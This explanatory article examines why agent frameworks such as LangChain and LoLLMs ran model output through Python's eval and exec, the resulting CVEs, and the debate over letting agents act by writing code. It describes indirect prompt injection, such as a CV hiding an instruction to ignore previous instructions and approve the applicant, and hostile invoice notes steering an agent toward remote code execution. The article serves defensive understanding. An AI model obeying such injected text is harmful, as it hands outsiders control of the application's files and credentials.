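# Why agent frameworks run model output as code, and the safer designs

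## What it means to run model output as code

An agent framework is a software library that sends prompts to a language model and acts on the output. Developers use frameworks such as LangChain, Microsoft's Semantic Kernel and Hugging Face's smolagents to build programs that query a database, draw a chart or send an email in response to a plain-language request. A model produces only text, so the framework has to turn that text into action. Frameworks have often done this by passing the text to a programming-language interpreter, usually Python's, which runs it with all the application's permissions. This is easy to implement, but it gives anyone who can steer the model's text a way to run programs on the application's machine. NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which tests AI systems before they go into production, counts this among the most serious problems it keeps finding.

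### The model, the framework and the tools

A large language model continues a text, called the prompt, by predicting which character, word or run of words is likely to come next. *Generative AI Models* (Alt, Ibisch and colleagues, 2025), a guide from Germany's Federal Office for Information Security, notes that the output can be natural language, a table or program code. The model produces all of these as text. If it writes a Python program that deletes a folder, the program does nothing until other software runs it. In *Anatomy of an LLM RCE*, Reiner (2024) looks for security weaknesses in the ordinary software around a model, because the model itself cannot run code.

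That software usually offers the model some tools. A tool is a function of the application that the model can request, and the prompt describes its name, purpose and inputs. For example, an agent might need to total the invoices more than 90 days overdue and email the total to the finance team. It has two tools: `list_invoices()`, which returns each invoice with its amount and age, and `send_email(to, body)`. The books hold an invoice of 1,200 that is 120 days overdue, one of 800 that is 95 days overdue and one of 500 that is 30 days overdue. Only the first two count, so the email should give a total of 2,000. Even this small task involves reading data, applying a condition, doing arithmetic and sending an email, which can't be undone.

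Reiner traces the path from text to action in LoLLMs, a program that gives users one interface to many models. LoLLMs sent the model a prompt that listed a function named `calculate`, with instructions to call it for any arithmetic. Each call had to be a short block of JSON, a standard notation for structured data, containing the function's name and parameters. Ordinary Python code then searched the model's reply for such blocks, parsed the JSON, looked up the name in a table of available functions and called the one it found. The result went back to the model, which wrote the final answer.

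So far, no interpreter had run the model's text. The model had made a structured tool call, in which the framework decides what each name refers to. But `calculate` then passed the model's expression, a string such as "1200 + 800", to Python's `eval` function, which ran it as code.

### What eval and exec do

A harmless use of `eval` fits on one line:

```python
eval("1200 + 800")   # gives 2000
```

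Python's `eval` function runs a string as an expression and returns the value. The related function `exec` runs a string as whole statements, including loops, imports and function definitions, and returns nothing.

Python can run model output as code because, in the words of O'Reilly's *Executing Commands and Evaluating Expressions*, "the interpreter is always available", so a running program can parse, compile and execute text it has just received. Several other languages can do this too, although the same passage calls the ability rare. MITRE's *CWE-95*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, lists JavaScript, Perl, PHP and Ruby alongside Python as languages where evaluating outside text can go wrong. A C program normally ships without its compiler, so it can't ordinarily run a string as C code.

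`eval` is dangerous because the text it runs has the same rights as the program that calls it. An operating system grants rights to a whole process, meaning a running program, and doesn't distinguish among the lines inside it. Once the interpreter has accepted a string, it treats the contents exactly as it treats the lines the developer wrote. Evaluated text can therefore open any file the process can open, connect to any machine it can reach, and read the passwords and access keys in its memory. OpenMV's *Dynamic code*, part of the manual for the OpenMV programmable camera, describes the reach of such input as "anything the calling script could do".

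The process that runs the invoice agent must hold logins for the accounting database and the mail server, because its two tools need them. The string "1200 + 800" uses neither login, but the call to `eval` would not stop a different string from using both. Python's official manual page, *Built-in functions*, says that evaluated text can by default even access the variables of the code that called `eval`. A developer can pass in a shorter list of names, as LoLLMs did for its calculator, but the manual says this is "not a security mechanism". Reiner got past the LoLLMs version, which its developers have since fixed.

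Both entries on that manual page now carry a warning that the function executes arbitrary code and that untrusted input will lead to vulnerabilities. The warning is fairly new. In May 2024, DanielRuf (2024), a GitHub user, reported that the entries had none, after reading a blog post about generative AI by the security company Snyk. Security specialists had known of the problem for much longer (MITRE's entry goes back to 2006), but a developer who looked up `eval` in the official documentation while building an early agent framework may well have found a description of the function with no warning.

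### Why model output counts as untrusted

The risk of evaluating a string as code depends on who can influence the string. If the developer typed it into the source code, `eval` adds no danger. A model's output depends on the whole prompt, which the developer seldom writes in full. Part of the prompt is the user's question, and much of the rest may be web pages, emails, documents or database records that the framework fetched.

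Prompt injection is text in a model's input that makes it follow an attacker's instructions. MITRE's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* attributes the flaw to how a product builds its prompts, which leaves the model unable to distinguish a user's input from the developer's directives. The attacker doesn't need an account on the system or any contact with it. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C describes a recruiter who uses a model to score job applications. A candidate hides a line in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection. The invoice agent is vulnerable too. If each invoice includes a note written by the customer, and the framework pastes the records into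 the prompt, any customer can add instructions to the prompt.

Older software had a similar problem and largely solved it. In SQL injection, an attacker types database commands into a field meant for a name or a date, and a careless program pastes them into a query. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the query and the values separately, so the database never treats a value as a command. David C argues that a language model can't be given the same separation, because it receives instructions and data alike as one sequence of tokens (short pieces of text) and predicts the next one. Developers can make attacks harder by marking outside text as data. They can also train models to give priority to the developer's instructions, or scan for suspicious phrases, though David C rates scanning poorly because an attacker can keep rephrasing a request. None of these methods fully separates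 instructions from data, and David C concludes that a complete fix may never come. That forecast could be wrong, but a program that evaluates model output with full rights is safe only if a complete fix already exists and works for every prompt.

When injected text reaches an interpreter, the result is remote code execution, which means an outsider can run code of their choice on someone else's machine. The first example in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, part of a widely used list of risks from the non-profit security foundation OWASP, is model output passed directly into a system shell, `exec` or `eval`. The consequences MITRE lists for evaluating input as code include reading restricted files and acting under someone else's identity. MITRE also notes that programs often keep no log of what the injected code did, so the owner may not find out.

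Developers who would never run a stranger's text as code may run a model's partly because it seems to come from their own application. MITRE's *CWE-1426*, the catalogue's entry on unchecked output from generative AI, compares many of these flaws to second-order SQL injection. In that attack, the attacker's text is first stored in the database as harmless data, then does damage when the application retrieves it and builds a query from it. By then the text looks like the application's own. MITRE also warns that developers rely on input filters and the model's training, and overestimate how well both work. The company that hosts the model can also send hostile text. One of the real flaws that MITRE lists under eval injection is in a framework for language-model applications, which a crafted response from a hosting provider could exploit.

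Calling model output untrusted means that the program has to stay safe whatever the text turns out to be, however good it usually is. OWASP advises treating the model like any other user and checking what it sends. David C cites a stricter rule from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model processing someone's information should have no more privileges than that person has. Evaluating the model's output inside the application breaks this rule. For example, the customer who wrote the invoice note has no right to the accounting login, but `eval` may let them get it through the model. This risk disappears only when no outsider can influence any part of the input, as when a developer works alone on private data. Even then, the model may write a bad program by mistake.

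Practitioners ranked prompt injection first in OWASP's 2026 list for the third time running, although Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reports relatively few recorded cases. Improper output handling came last of the ten risks, according to SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications*. That low rank is little reassurance to the owner of an application that runs model output as code, because the list covers every kind of application built on a language model, including those that never do this. Steve Wilson, who founded the list, said in OWASP's announcement (2026) that security work should assume AI will sometimes be fooled and should put enforceable controls around what it can reach.

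### Review, deliberate execution and incidental evaluation

Some programs ask a model for code but leave it to a person to run. A bookkeeper might ask a chat assistant for a script that totals overdue invoices, then read the script before deciding whether to use it. This still has risks. OWASP describes a software company whose developers generate code from plain-language requests. The code may contain a security hole, or it may call for a software package that the model made up, and a developer who looks for that package may download something malicious. OWASP recommends careful review, though a hurried reader may miss the flaw.

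Deliberate execution takes the person away. It means running a program that the developer asked the model to write. For the invoice task, the model might reply with two lines:

```python
total = sum(i.amount for i in list_invoices() if i.days_overdue > 90)
send_email("finance@example.com", f"Overdue more than 90 days: {total}")
```

The framework passes the model's code to `exec`, and the finance team receives 2,000. The developer intended a program to run. NVIDIA's team has seen the same design in applications that have a model write code to draw a plot.

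Incidental evaluation is running model text that the developer meant as data, using the interpreter only as a convenient way to read a value. Suppose ordinary code fetches the invoices and sends the email, and the developer asks the model only which amounts qualify. The model replies with the string "1200, 800". The program needs numbers it can add, and `eval` will produce them, as in the Python manual's example of `eval("1, 2")` returning a pair of numbers. MITRE's catalogue includes almost the same mistake in a short script that asks a user for a comma-separated list and evaluates the answer to sum it. Snyk's *Code injection vulnerabilities caused by generative AI*, the post that prompted the complaint about Python's manual, describes a version with a language model, in which the program asks for a reply in JSON and reads it with `eval`.

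Calculators are harder to classify. LoLLMs needed only to do arithmetic, as did LangChain's math component, which, according to the catalogue text in Mondoo's *CWE 94*, turned a user's question into a Python expression and passed it to `exec`. An arithmetic expression is a kind of code, and the developers did intend to evaluate it, but they did so in a way that allowed any Python code to run. Calculators are therefore closer to incidental evaluation, since a much more limited evaluator would have given the same answers.

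How hard the flaw is to fix depends on whether the program evaluates code incidentally or deliberately. MITRE's first recommendation for eval injection is to rewrite the program so that it does not need `eval`, which is easy when the evaluation is incidental. The summing script can split its input at the commas and convert each piece with `int`, which raises an error on anything that is not a whole number. The JSON reader can call `json.loads`, a standard function that parses the notation without running anything. Both programs still do everything they did before. When running code is the purpose, the same advice would remove the feature along with the flaw, so a developer who wants to keep the feature has to limit what the code can reach while it runs.

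## How arithmetic and data questions led frameworks to exec

Arithmetic gave early agent frameworks a strong reason to run model-written code. The language models of 2022 could often work out which sums a question called for, but then got them wrong. A Python interpreter does arithmetic reliably, so researchers and hobbyists began asking models for short programs and running them. LangChain, which Harrison Chase released as an open-source project in October 2022, offered ready-made components for this, several of which passed the model's text to `exec`.

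### Right steps, wrong sums

In 2022 the usual way to have a model solve a word problem was chain-of-thought prompting. The prompt includes a few examples with the working written out in prose, and the model imitates them, doing both the planning and the arithmetic. Gao, Madaan and colleagues (2022), in *PAL*, tested how well this worked with larger numbers. They replaced one number in each question of GSM8K, a set of grade-school word problems, with a random integer of up to seven digits. The accuracy of Codex, OpenAI's model for writing code, fell from 65.6% to 23.1%. The team then compared the model's working on the original and harder versions of 25 questions. In 16 of them the reasoning was nearly identical, so in most cases the model had planned the harder problem as well as before but got the arithmetic wrong.

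Models can get long calculations wrong even when the numbers are small. *Program of Thoughts Prompting* (Chen, Ma and colleagues, 2022) gives the hypothetical example of a model that gets each addition right 90% of the time. Its chance of getting 50 additions in a row right is 0.9⁵⁰, or about 0.5%.

Both teams had the model write a program and left the calculation to Python. One of the example problems in *PAL* concerns Olivia, who has $23 and buys five bagels at $3 each. How much money does she have left? A chain-of-thought prompt would give the working in words and then the answer, 8. A PAL prompt pairs each example question with a short program and leaves the answer out, so the model has no pattern to follow for stating results itself. The new question goes at the end of the prompt. If the new question were Olivia's, the model might reply:

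```python
cash = 23
bagel_count = 5
price_each = 3
spent = bagel_count * price_each
answer = cash - spent
```

Ordinary software passes this text to the interpreter, which computes `spent` as 15 and `answer` as 8. The software then reports `answer`. If Olivia had $6,405,118 instead, only the first line would change, and the subtraction would be just as reliable.

Both papers report large gains for Codex:

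| Test | Chain of thought | Program run by Python | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| GSM8K (word problems) | 65.6% | 72.0% | Gao and colleagues |
| GSM-Hard (the same, with one large number) | 23.1% | 61.2% | Gao and colleagues |
| Object Counting (counting items of one kind) | 73.0% | 96.7% | Gao and colleagues |
| FinQA (questions on financial tables and text) | 40.4% | 64.5% | Chen and colleagues |
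| ConvFinQA (similar questions in a conversation) | 45.6% | 64.6% | Chen and colleagues |

The interpreter accounts for most of the gain. When Gao and colleagues had the model write a program and then predict its output instead of running it, the model solved only 23.2% of GSM8K problems.

These figures are now out of date. A later version of the paper by Chen and colleagues includes GPT-4, which solved 92.0% of GSM8K with chain of thought alone and 97.2% with programs. On FinQA, where the numbers can run into the millions, the gap was still wide, with 58.2% solved by chain of thought and 74.0% with programs.

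An interpreter can't correct a wrong plan. In the example that opens *PAL*, a bakery bakes 200 loaves, sells 132 and gets six back from a shop. The chain-of-thought reply subtracts the six returned loaves instead of adding them, and arrives at 62 instead of 74. Its arithmetic is correct, so Python would have given the same answer from the same plan. Chen and colleagues examined 198 of their method's failures on another set of financial questions. In 47% the program used wrong values, in 33% it had the wrong logic, and in a further 15% it had both faults.

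It is less clear that the method needed all of Python. Researchers had already tried attaching a calculator that rechecked the equations in a model's prose, but Chen and colleagues found that this raised Codex's score on GSM8K only from 63.1% to 65.4%, compared with 71.6% when it wrote programs. They attributed the small gain to the rigid step that matched the calculator's results to the prose. Gao and colleagues preferred Python to small purpose-built languages because many models had trained on Python. That is a sensible reason, but the main experiments in the two papers didn't compare Python with a small language that had only variables and arithmetic, which is all Olivia's program uses. Some other tasks did use more, since the counting problems used Python's dictionaries and Chen and colleagues solved equations with SymPy, an algebra library.

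Chen and colleagues also warned that running generated code was dangerous because it could delete files, so they stopped programs from importing modules outside an approved set. They thought this worked reasonably well for mathematics but might get in the way on other tasks. The pseudo-code at the end of their paper runs the program with a single call to `exec`.

### From a demonstration to a library

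Hobbyists had reached the same idea slightly earlier. On 10 September 2022 Riley Goodside, posting on Twitter as goodside (2022), shared a prompt that began "You are GPT-3, and you can't do math" and had the model use a Python interpreter for calculations. Goodside said the idea wasn't new, and that what was new, if anything, was doing it with instructions alone, without further training. As the post spread, Goodside warned readers not to try it "outside of a security sandbox", because a model given the prompt would delete a hard drive if asked.

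Two days later the AI researcher Sergey Karayev published a similar demonstration, thanking Goodside and Amjad Masad, a co-founder of the browser-based programming service Replit. The Decoder's *AI researchers push GPT-3's boundaries with Python* reported that the interpreter ran in the cloud and that Karayev strongly advised against running the experiment on a local computer.

LangChain's first calculator, LLMMathChain, came from this line of work. A "chain" in LangChain is a fixed sequence of steps. LangChain's *llm_math*, the project's note on the module, describes it as "heavily borrowed" from a program Masad had posted on Replit. LangChain's *LLM Math*, an early documentation page, includes a sample prompt that opens with the same sentence as Goodside's. The example problem is to raise 13 to the power of 0.3432. The model writes two lines of Python that import the `math` module and print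 the result, and the chain runs them and returns 2.41.

An early version of LangChain's LLMMathChain checked whether the model's reply started with the marks that open a block of Python code. If it did, the chain stripped the marks and passed the code between them to another component to run, without checking what the code would do. If the reply started with "Answer", the chain returned it unchanged. Any other reply caused an error.

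LangChain's *PAL* page describes PALChain as an implementation of a research method by Gao and colleagues and demonstrates it on a word problem about three people's pets. As described in LangChain's *Utility Chains*, the two chains worked almost identically. Each turned a question into Python and ran it in a REPL, an interpreter that runs code and returns the output.

Questions about data led to the same design. A data frame is a table that a program holds in memory, and pandas is the Python library that most people use for handling one. LangChain built agents that let a user question such a table in plain language. Suppose the three invoices from the earlier example sit in a data frame called `df`, and the bookkeeper asks how much is more than 90 days overdue. The model can answer with one line:

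```python
df[df.days_overdue > 90].amount.sum()   # gives 2000
```

The data-frame agent passed such lines to a Python tool. The American consumer organisation Consumer Reports examined the tool's code with the security firm Include Security while testing ways to query its own product ratings, and describes the code in *Who's Verifying the Verifier*. The tool ran everything except the last line with `exec`, then ran the last line with `eval` to get a value. Its cleaning function only removed spaces, backticks and the word "python" from around the code. By 2024 LangChain listed agents of this kind for CSV files, pandas, Spark and xorbits.

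A much narrower evaluator would have been enough for the calculator, but not for the other components. A data-frame agent has to run pandas code, and pandas can read and write files. PALChain also had to run programs, because its method was to have the model write them.

### Warnings, scores and a change of address

Users warned about the danger of `exec` in LLMMathChain in issues 814 and 1026 on LangChain's public issue tracker. Commenters on issue 1026 suggested several ways to run the code in a sandbox, which limits what a program can access.

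In April 2023 the flaw received a CVE number. A CVE number identifies a specific flaw in a specific product, whereas the CWE entries in MITRE's catalogue describe kinds of flaw. GitLab's *CVE-2023-29374* (2023) says that LLMMathChain, in LangChain versions through 0.0.131, allowed prompt injection that could execute arbitrary code through `exec`. It rates the flaw's severity 9.8 out of 10. The score assumes an attacker who works over a network, has no account and needs no help from a user. It fits a public chatbot with a calculator but overstates the risk to somebody doing sums alone on a laptop, although LangChain's developers couldn't know which kind of application users would build.

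According to Consumer Reports, a contributor first proposed fixing the flaw by replacing `exec` with `eval`. Other developers pointed out that this stopped some of the attacks in the original report but still let an attacker run system commands. LangChain eventually switched LLMMathChain to numexpr, a library for evaluating numerical expressions. Safety, a vulnerability database, lists version 0.0.142 as the fix, but in May 2026 GitLab's page still listed the flaw as having no solution available.

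PALChain received its own CVE in July 2023. GitLab's *CVE-2023-36258* (2023) again names `exec` and gives a score of 9.8. This time LangChain moved the code to a new package, `langchain_experimental`. On 21 July a commit titled "remove CVEs" copied PALChain there, along with a component that ran database queries and a function that loaded prompts from Python files. LangChain (2023) promised "Zero changes to functionality" in the commit message. The old copies were to stay in the main package for another week so that users could switch.

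LangChain had said in a public discussion that the plan would make the core package smaller and free of CVEs, and let contributors share experiments without anyone mistaking them for production code. The plan covered all chains and agents that executed arbitrary SQL or Python. One user replied that their application already relied on the SQL and pandas agents and asked how much disruption to expect.

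Separating the packages helped somewhat, because developers now had to install something with "experimental" in its name to get the risky parts. But it didn't protect those who installed it, since PALChain still ran model-written programs. LangChain had added a check on the generated code, but its *pal_chain* reference page describes the chain as vulnerable to arbitrary code execution.

Moving the code also made the vulnerability databases misleading. The Python tool behind the data-frame agents also had a CVE. GitLab's *CVE-2023-39659* (2023) lists versions before 0.0.325 as affected, so a developer could reasonably assume that upgrading fixed the problem. Include Security traced the change through the source code and found that LangChain had described the tool as deprecated but had moved it to the experimental package, where attackers could still exploit it. Consumer Reports then reconsidered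 whether it needed a Python interpreter at all and began trying other approaches.

### Why LangChain used exec

LangChain (2023) wrote in a blog post on 31 July that the project "started off as highly experimental" and included features such as code execution because they were "pushing boundary of what was possible". The record supports this account, although a company has reason to describe its past mistakes generously, especially in a post titled "Goodbye CVEs". According to LangChain's module note, the calculator came from a demonstration. The PAL results also show that running code solved a real problem.

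Copying a demonstration into a library also changed where the code ran. Karayev's interpreter ran in the cloud and Masad's program ran on Replit, but LangChain's version ran wherever a developer had installed the library, often beside the application's files and passwords. LangChain seems to have lost the sandbox this way, though nobody there has said so. Ignorance of the risk is a weaker explanation, because Goodside and Karayev had both published warnings about `exec`, even if Python's manual had none.

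Another possible reason is that models had no standard interface for tool calls. LangChain's early code worked without one. LLMMathChain searched free text for code marks, and vgel.me, a programming blog, describes LangChain agents that called a Python interpreter through a special text syntax. The blog also shows GPT-3 giving a memorised answer instead of using its own code. LangChain's *LLMMathChain* reference page now lists tool calling first among the benefits of the chain's replacement.

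But the missing interface explains only how the model's text reached the framework. LoLLMs, the program Reiner studied, had a structured call for its calculator and still passed the expression to `eval`. The replacement for LLMMathChain also receives an expression as a string, and a developer still has to choose what evaluates it, such as numexpr in LangChain's example.

Convenience probably mattered more. Running a program with `exec` takes one line, as in the pseudo-code by Chen and colleagues, and the rest of LLMMathChain is not much longer. Developers may have chosen `exec` for this brevity, but that is an inference from the code. A call to numexpr is about as short, so convenience alone can't explain why the calculator used `exec`. Copying a working demonstration explains that choice better. Convenience is a stronger explanation for PALChain and the data-frame agents, which needed variables,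 functions or pandas, because no safe substitute was nearly as short.

The work of building a sandbox helps explain why `exec` stayed after people complained about it. Consumer Reports recounts discussions of a restricted version of Python, a stripped-down container and WebAssembly, a format for running programs in isolation. Three threads went quiet, and an automated assistant then closed them with nothing resolved. The proposals probably lapsed because people install a library like LangChain on laptops, servers and shared notebooks, and a sandbox that suited all of them would have made the library much harder to install and maintain. Consumer Reports suggests a simpler reason, that developers of language-model tools prefer new features and quick wins to the hardest problems.

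### The components in 2026

LangChain has deprecated LLMMathChain and plans to remove it in version 2.0.0. It tells developers to build an agent with a calculator tool instead. The chain is still in `langchain-classic`, a package of older code that gets security fixes only until December 2026, according to LangChain's *Chains* page.

LangChain says on the experimental package's download page that it is retiring this package too, and warns that parts of it may be dangerous outside a sandbox. In June 2026, Ecosyste.ms, a service that tracks open-source software, listed the code repository as archived and no longer maintained, with its last update on 22 May. It also counted about 2.5 million downloads in the previous month and 51 other packages that depended on the experimental package. Download counts include automated installations, and many of the package's users may never use PALChain or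 the data-frame agents. Those who do can't expect LangChain to fix new flaws.

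## The case for letting models act by writing code

The calculators and data-frame agents of 2022 and 2023 ran code to answer questions. Researchers soon proposed that an agent should take every action this way, by writing a short program that calls its tools. Such a program is known as a code action, and the usual alternative is a series of structured tool calls.

The case for letting models act by writing code rests on five premises. A program can combine several steps, keep intermediate results in variables, and do things that no tool designer planned for. Models have seen far more code than tool calls in training, and one program can replace several calls to the model, which saves time and tokens. Each premise is at least partly true, but each faces a serious objection, and the results of experiments in 2026 are more mixed than the blog posts that popularized the idea suggest.

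### The invoice task done both ways

With structured tool calls, the invoice agent has to call the model three times. On the first call, the model requests `list_invoices()`, and the framework runs the function and adds the three invoices to the prompt. On the second, the model picks out the two invoices that are more than 90 days overdue, adds 1,200 and 800 itself, and requests `send_email` with the total. On the third, it reads the confirmation and tells the user the email was sent.

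With a code action, two model calls are enough. In the first, the model writes the two-line script from the earlier example, and the framework runs it in Python to compute the sum. In the second, the model reads the result and tells the user.

Saving one call isn't much, but the savings grow with the task. Suppose the finance team wants a separate reminder sent to each of 40 overdue customers. Many models can request several tools in one reply, so the number of model calls might stay at three, but the model would have to write out all 40 requests instead of one short loop in a script. Looking up each customer's address first would add another model call to the tool-call version but only another line to the script.

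### CodeAct

*Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2024) named this approach CodeAct and tested it on 17 models, from small versions of Llama 2 to GPT-4. Each model wrote its actions in Python, in JSON and as text in a fixed pattern.

One experiment used API-Bank, an existing collection of tool-use tasks, and asked for a single tool call per task. With no calls to combine, any advantage for Python had to come from the models' familiarity with it. Most models did about as well with Python as with the other formats, or better. JSON was consistently the weakest format for the open-source models, but the commercial models did decently with it, and the researchers suspected that these models had been trained on it.

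The other experiment tested combination. The team wrote 82 tasks in areas such as finance, travel planning and web browsing, most of which needed several calls to several tools. A model had up to ten turns to find the answer, and its Python could include loops and conditions. These are some of the success rates:

| Model | Python | JSON | Text |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4 (November 2023 preview) | 74.4% | 52.4% | 53.7% |
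| GPT-4 (June 2023) | 67.1% | 56.1% | 45.1% |
| Claude 2 | 54.9% | 39.0% | 29.3% |
| Claude Instant 1 | 20.7% | 31.7% | 24.4% |
| Lemur 70B | 13.4% | 15.9% | 12.2% |
| CodeLlama 13B | 4.9% | 4.9% | 4.9% |

The paper's often-quoted gain of up to 20 percentage points comes from the top row, where Python scored 20.7 points higher than text, the next best format. The model in that row also needed fewer turns with Python, averaging 5.5 compared with 7.7 for text.

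JSON matched or beat Python for seven of the 17 models. Wang and colleagues count Python as the best format for 12, but two of those were ties, and in one of the ties every format scored zero. Most of those seven were weak models that solved almost no tasks in any format. Claude Instant is a stronger counterexample, since it solved 26 tasks with JSON and 17 with Python.

The benchmark was small and came from the team proposing the method, and the models are now long out of date, but the pattern is still informative. The strongest models gained the most from Python, and their gains came on tasks that required combining steps. Wang and colleagues expected the advantage to widen as models improved.

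### Saving model calls and tokens

CodeAct's agents had few tools. By 2025, developers were connecting agents to hundreds of them through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic launched in November 2024. A program that offers tools through MCP is called an MCP server. Most agents put the description of every available tool into the prompt, then add the result of every tool call. This text makes agents slower and more expensive to run, and it fills the context window, the limited amount of text a model can take in at once.

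In September 2025 Varda and Pai proposed a remedy in *Code Mode*, a post on the blog of Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company. Their software turns the tools into a library of functions in TypeScript, a variant of JavaScript, and gives the model a single tool that runs code. Carey gives token figures in a later post on the same blog, also called *Code Mode*. Cloudflare's own programming interface has more than 2,500 operations, and describing each one as a tool would take 1.17 million tokens. A server with just two tools, one for searching the interface's specification and one for running code against it, takes about 1,000, or 99.9% fewer. That count leaves out the tokens the model uses when it searches, and the 1.17 million is hypothetical because, according to Carey, it exceeds the context window of the most advanced models. Cloudflare turns the method on by default in a product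 that puts several MCP servers behind one address, according to its *Code mode for MCP server portals* (2026).

Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* made a similar case in November 2025. In its example, a user asks an agent to copy a meeting transcript from Google Drive into a customer record. With tool calls, the model reads the whole transcript from one tool and writes it out again for another, which could add 50,000 tokens for a two-hour meeting. In a program, a variable carries the transcript from one function to the next. Willison (2025), in *Code execution with MCP*, considered these extra tokens a subtler problem than the tokens used by tool descriptions, which people had already discussed widely. Anthropic's headline figure, a 98.7% cut from 150,000 tokens to 2,000, comes from letting the agent read only the tool descriptions it needs. The post describes no experiment behind this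 figure.

Later that month Anthropic offered the method to developers as programmatic tool calling, which Navid (2025) demonstrated in *Programmatic tool calling (PTC)*. Claude writes code that calls the developer's tools from a container, an isolated environment for running programs. Anthropic has since reported much smaller savings from testing. *Building agents that reach production systems with MCP* (2026) puts the reduction at roughly 37% on complex workflows. The feature's documentation, *Programmatic tool calling*, reports better results on two web research benchmarks, and its Chinese edition, *程式化工具呼叫*, gives the average improvement as 11%, with 24% fewer input tokens. These are still a vendor's figures for its own product, but they are probably a better guide to what developers can expect than 98.7% or 99.9%.

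An agent can get much of the saving without code by searching for relevant tools, loading only their descriptions, and calling them with JSON as before. According to Anthropic's 2026 post, this alone tends to remove more than 85% of the tokens spent on tool descriptions.

Rai (2026), in *Beyond Plain MCP*, measured the effects of tool selection and code separately. The study gave three open-weight models, which anyone can download and run, 119 tasks in a simulated company with 42 tools for things like billing, calendars and customer records. In some runs, a small additional model first picked the few tools each task needed. With Qwen3.8-27B as the agent, this cut average token use per task from 26,602 to 15,099. Letting Qwen also write code cut it to 5,703, and Qwen's success rate rose from 82.4% to 98.3%. Tool selection accounted for a little over half of the token savings, and code for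 the rest.

Writing code helps less on small tasks. Pydantic, a company that makes Python tools, published a comparison to promote Monty, its interpreter for model-written code. Pydantic asked Claude Sonnet 4.5 to compare the weather in London and Paris using three tools. The first finds a city's coordinates, the second turns coordinates into a temperature, and the third turns the temperature into a description. Because the tools had to run in that order, the tool-call version took three rounds of requests and a final summary.

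| | Tool calls | One script |
|---|---|---|
| Model calls | 4 | 2 |
| Time | 12.2 s | 9.1 s |
| Input tokens | 4,100 | 3,300 |
| Output tokens | 480 | 493 |
| Cost | $0.019 | $0.017 |

Halving the model calls saved about a quarter of the time and a tenth of the cost. The model wrote slightly more text because the script was longer than the tool calls it replaced. Pydantic calls the saving modest and says it grows as tasks get more complex. These figures come from a single run by the tool's maker, and ordinary variation in response times could account for some of the three seconds saved.

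Code can even use more tokens than JSON. Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026), in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, found that the instructions for writing code added a fixed number of tokens to each prompt. On tasks that needed many independent calls, code used fewer tokens only above about 26 calls. At 48 calls, it used 3,535 tokens and JSON used 5,097. Few everyday requests need 26 calls, although the break-even point would be lower with tools that return long results, unlike those in this test.

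### Intermediate results that the model never sees

Keeping results in variables has benefits besides lower cost. Anthropic's post describes a script that filters a spreadsheet of 10,000 rows and shows the model five. With the same technique, a script can move customers' contact details from one system to another without the model reading them. In the invoice task, customers' notes on their invoices stay out of the prompt unless the script prints them, so a hostile note has less chance to steer the model.

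The drawback is that the model has to write the program before it sees the data. The invoice script assumes each invoice has fields called `amount` and `days_overdue`. If the description of `list_invoices` doesn't mention them, the model has to guess, and a wrong guess stops the program. With a tool call, the model can read the field names in the result.

Rai tested how much this matters by running the code version with and without a short note on what each tool returns:

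| Model | JSON tool calls | Code, no notes | Code with notes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 97.5% | 99.2% |
| Gemma-4-26B | 86.6% | 66.4% | 89.1% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 16.0% | 55.5% |

Without the notes, code was worse than JSON for two of the three models. With them, code was clearly better for Qwen and Nemotron, while Gemma's small gain could have been due to chance. Rai wrote the notes by hand and adjusted them on practice tasks, so a developer who connects an agent to other people's MCP servers may not have anything as good. The simulated tools also returned results instantly, unlike real ones. Even so, the experiment suggests that some comparisons of code with JSON have measured how well the tools were documented.

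Good documentation doesn't help when the right next step depends on what is in the data. Suppose the note on the 800 invoice explains that the customer paid last week. A model reading the list might leave that invoice out or ask the user about it, but the script would add it to the total and send the email. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026) reports this kind of difference between the two methods on tasks from ten MCP servers. Code took far fewer turns and fewer tokens, and the quality of the results was similar overall. But step-by-step calls sometimes did better at reading and summarising text from Wikipedia or Reddit. On some tasks spanning three servers, the program failed because the model had left out a condition that it could have discovered along the way.

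A code-writing agent can avoid this by printing the invoices, reading them, and then writing a second program that sends the email. That takes three model calls, the same as with structured tool calls. It also puts the customers' notes back into the prompt, because the model has to see data to judge it.

### Combining steps

Loops and conditions help less when a developer has already combined the steps into one tool. With a tool called `email_overdue_total(days)`, the invoice agent could do the whole job with one structured call and two model calls, the same number of model calls as the script needs. In a 2026 post, Anthropic recommends combined tools for most MCP servers, saying that a single tool for turning a discussion thread into an issue report works better than four smaller ones that the agent has to string together. It recommends code for services with hundreds of operations, where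 nobody could anticipate every useful combination. The case for code is therefore strongest for open-ended agents, while an application that repeats the same few tasks every day may gain nothing from it.

Experiments with recent models give weaker support for this premise than CodeAct did. Patel and colleagues tested 14 models from OpenAI and Anthropic on 52 tasks, each a chain of two to 20 calls. Code scored higher for six models and JSON for seven, with one tie. Claude Sonnet 5 rose from 80.8% with JSON to 96.2% with code, while the smaller Claude Haiku 4.5 fell from 88.5% to 73.1%. The test's design probably hurt code, because its functions only returned their own inputs, so a program couldn't pass a real result from one step to the next. The model had to work out the intermediate values itself, which removed one of the main reasons for writing a program.

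The same study found a clearer advantage for code when a task needed many separate calls at once. With JSON, Claude Sonnet 5 made every required call up to 70, began to miss some at 72, and failed completely at 100. With code, it made all 100. GPT-5.6-Sol made all 100 even with JSON, so the limit seems to come from particular models rather than from JSON itself.

### Familiarity with code

Varda and Pai argue that models write code better than tool calls because they have seen much more code in training. Their training data includes code from millions of open-source projects, while most of the examples of tool calls are artificial ones made by the models' developers. Varda and Pai compare using tool calls to giving Shakespeare a month of Mandarin lessons and then asking him to write a play in Mandarin.

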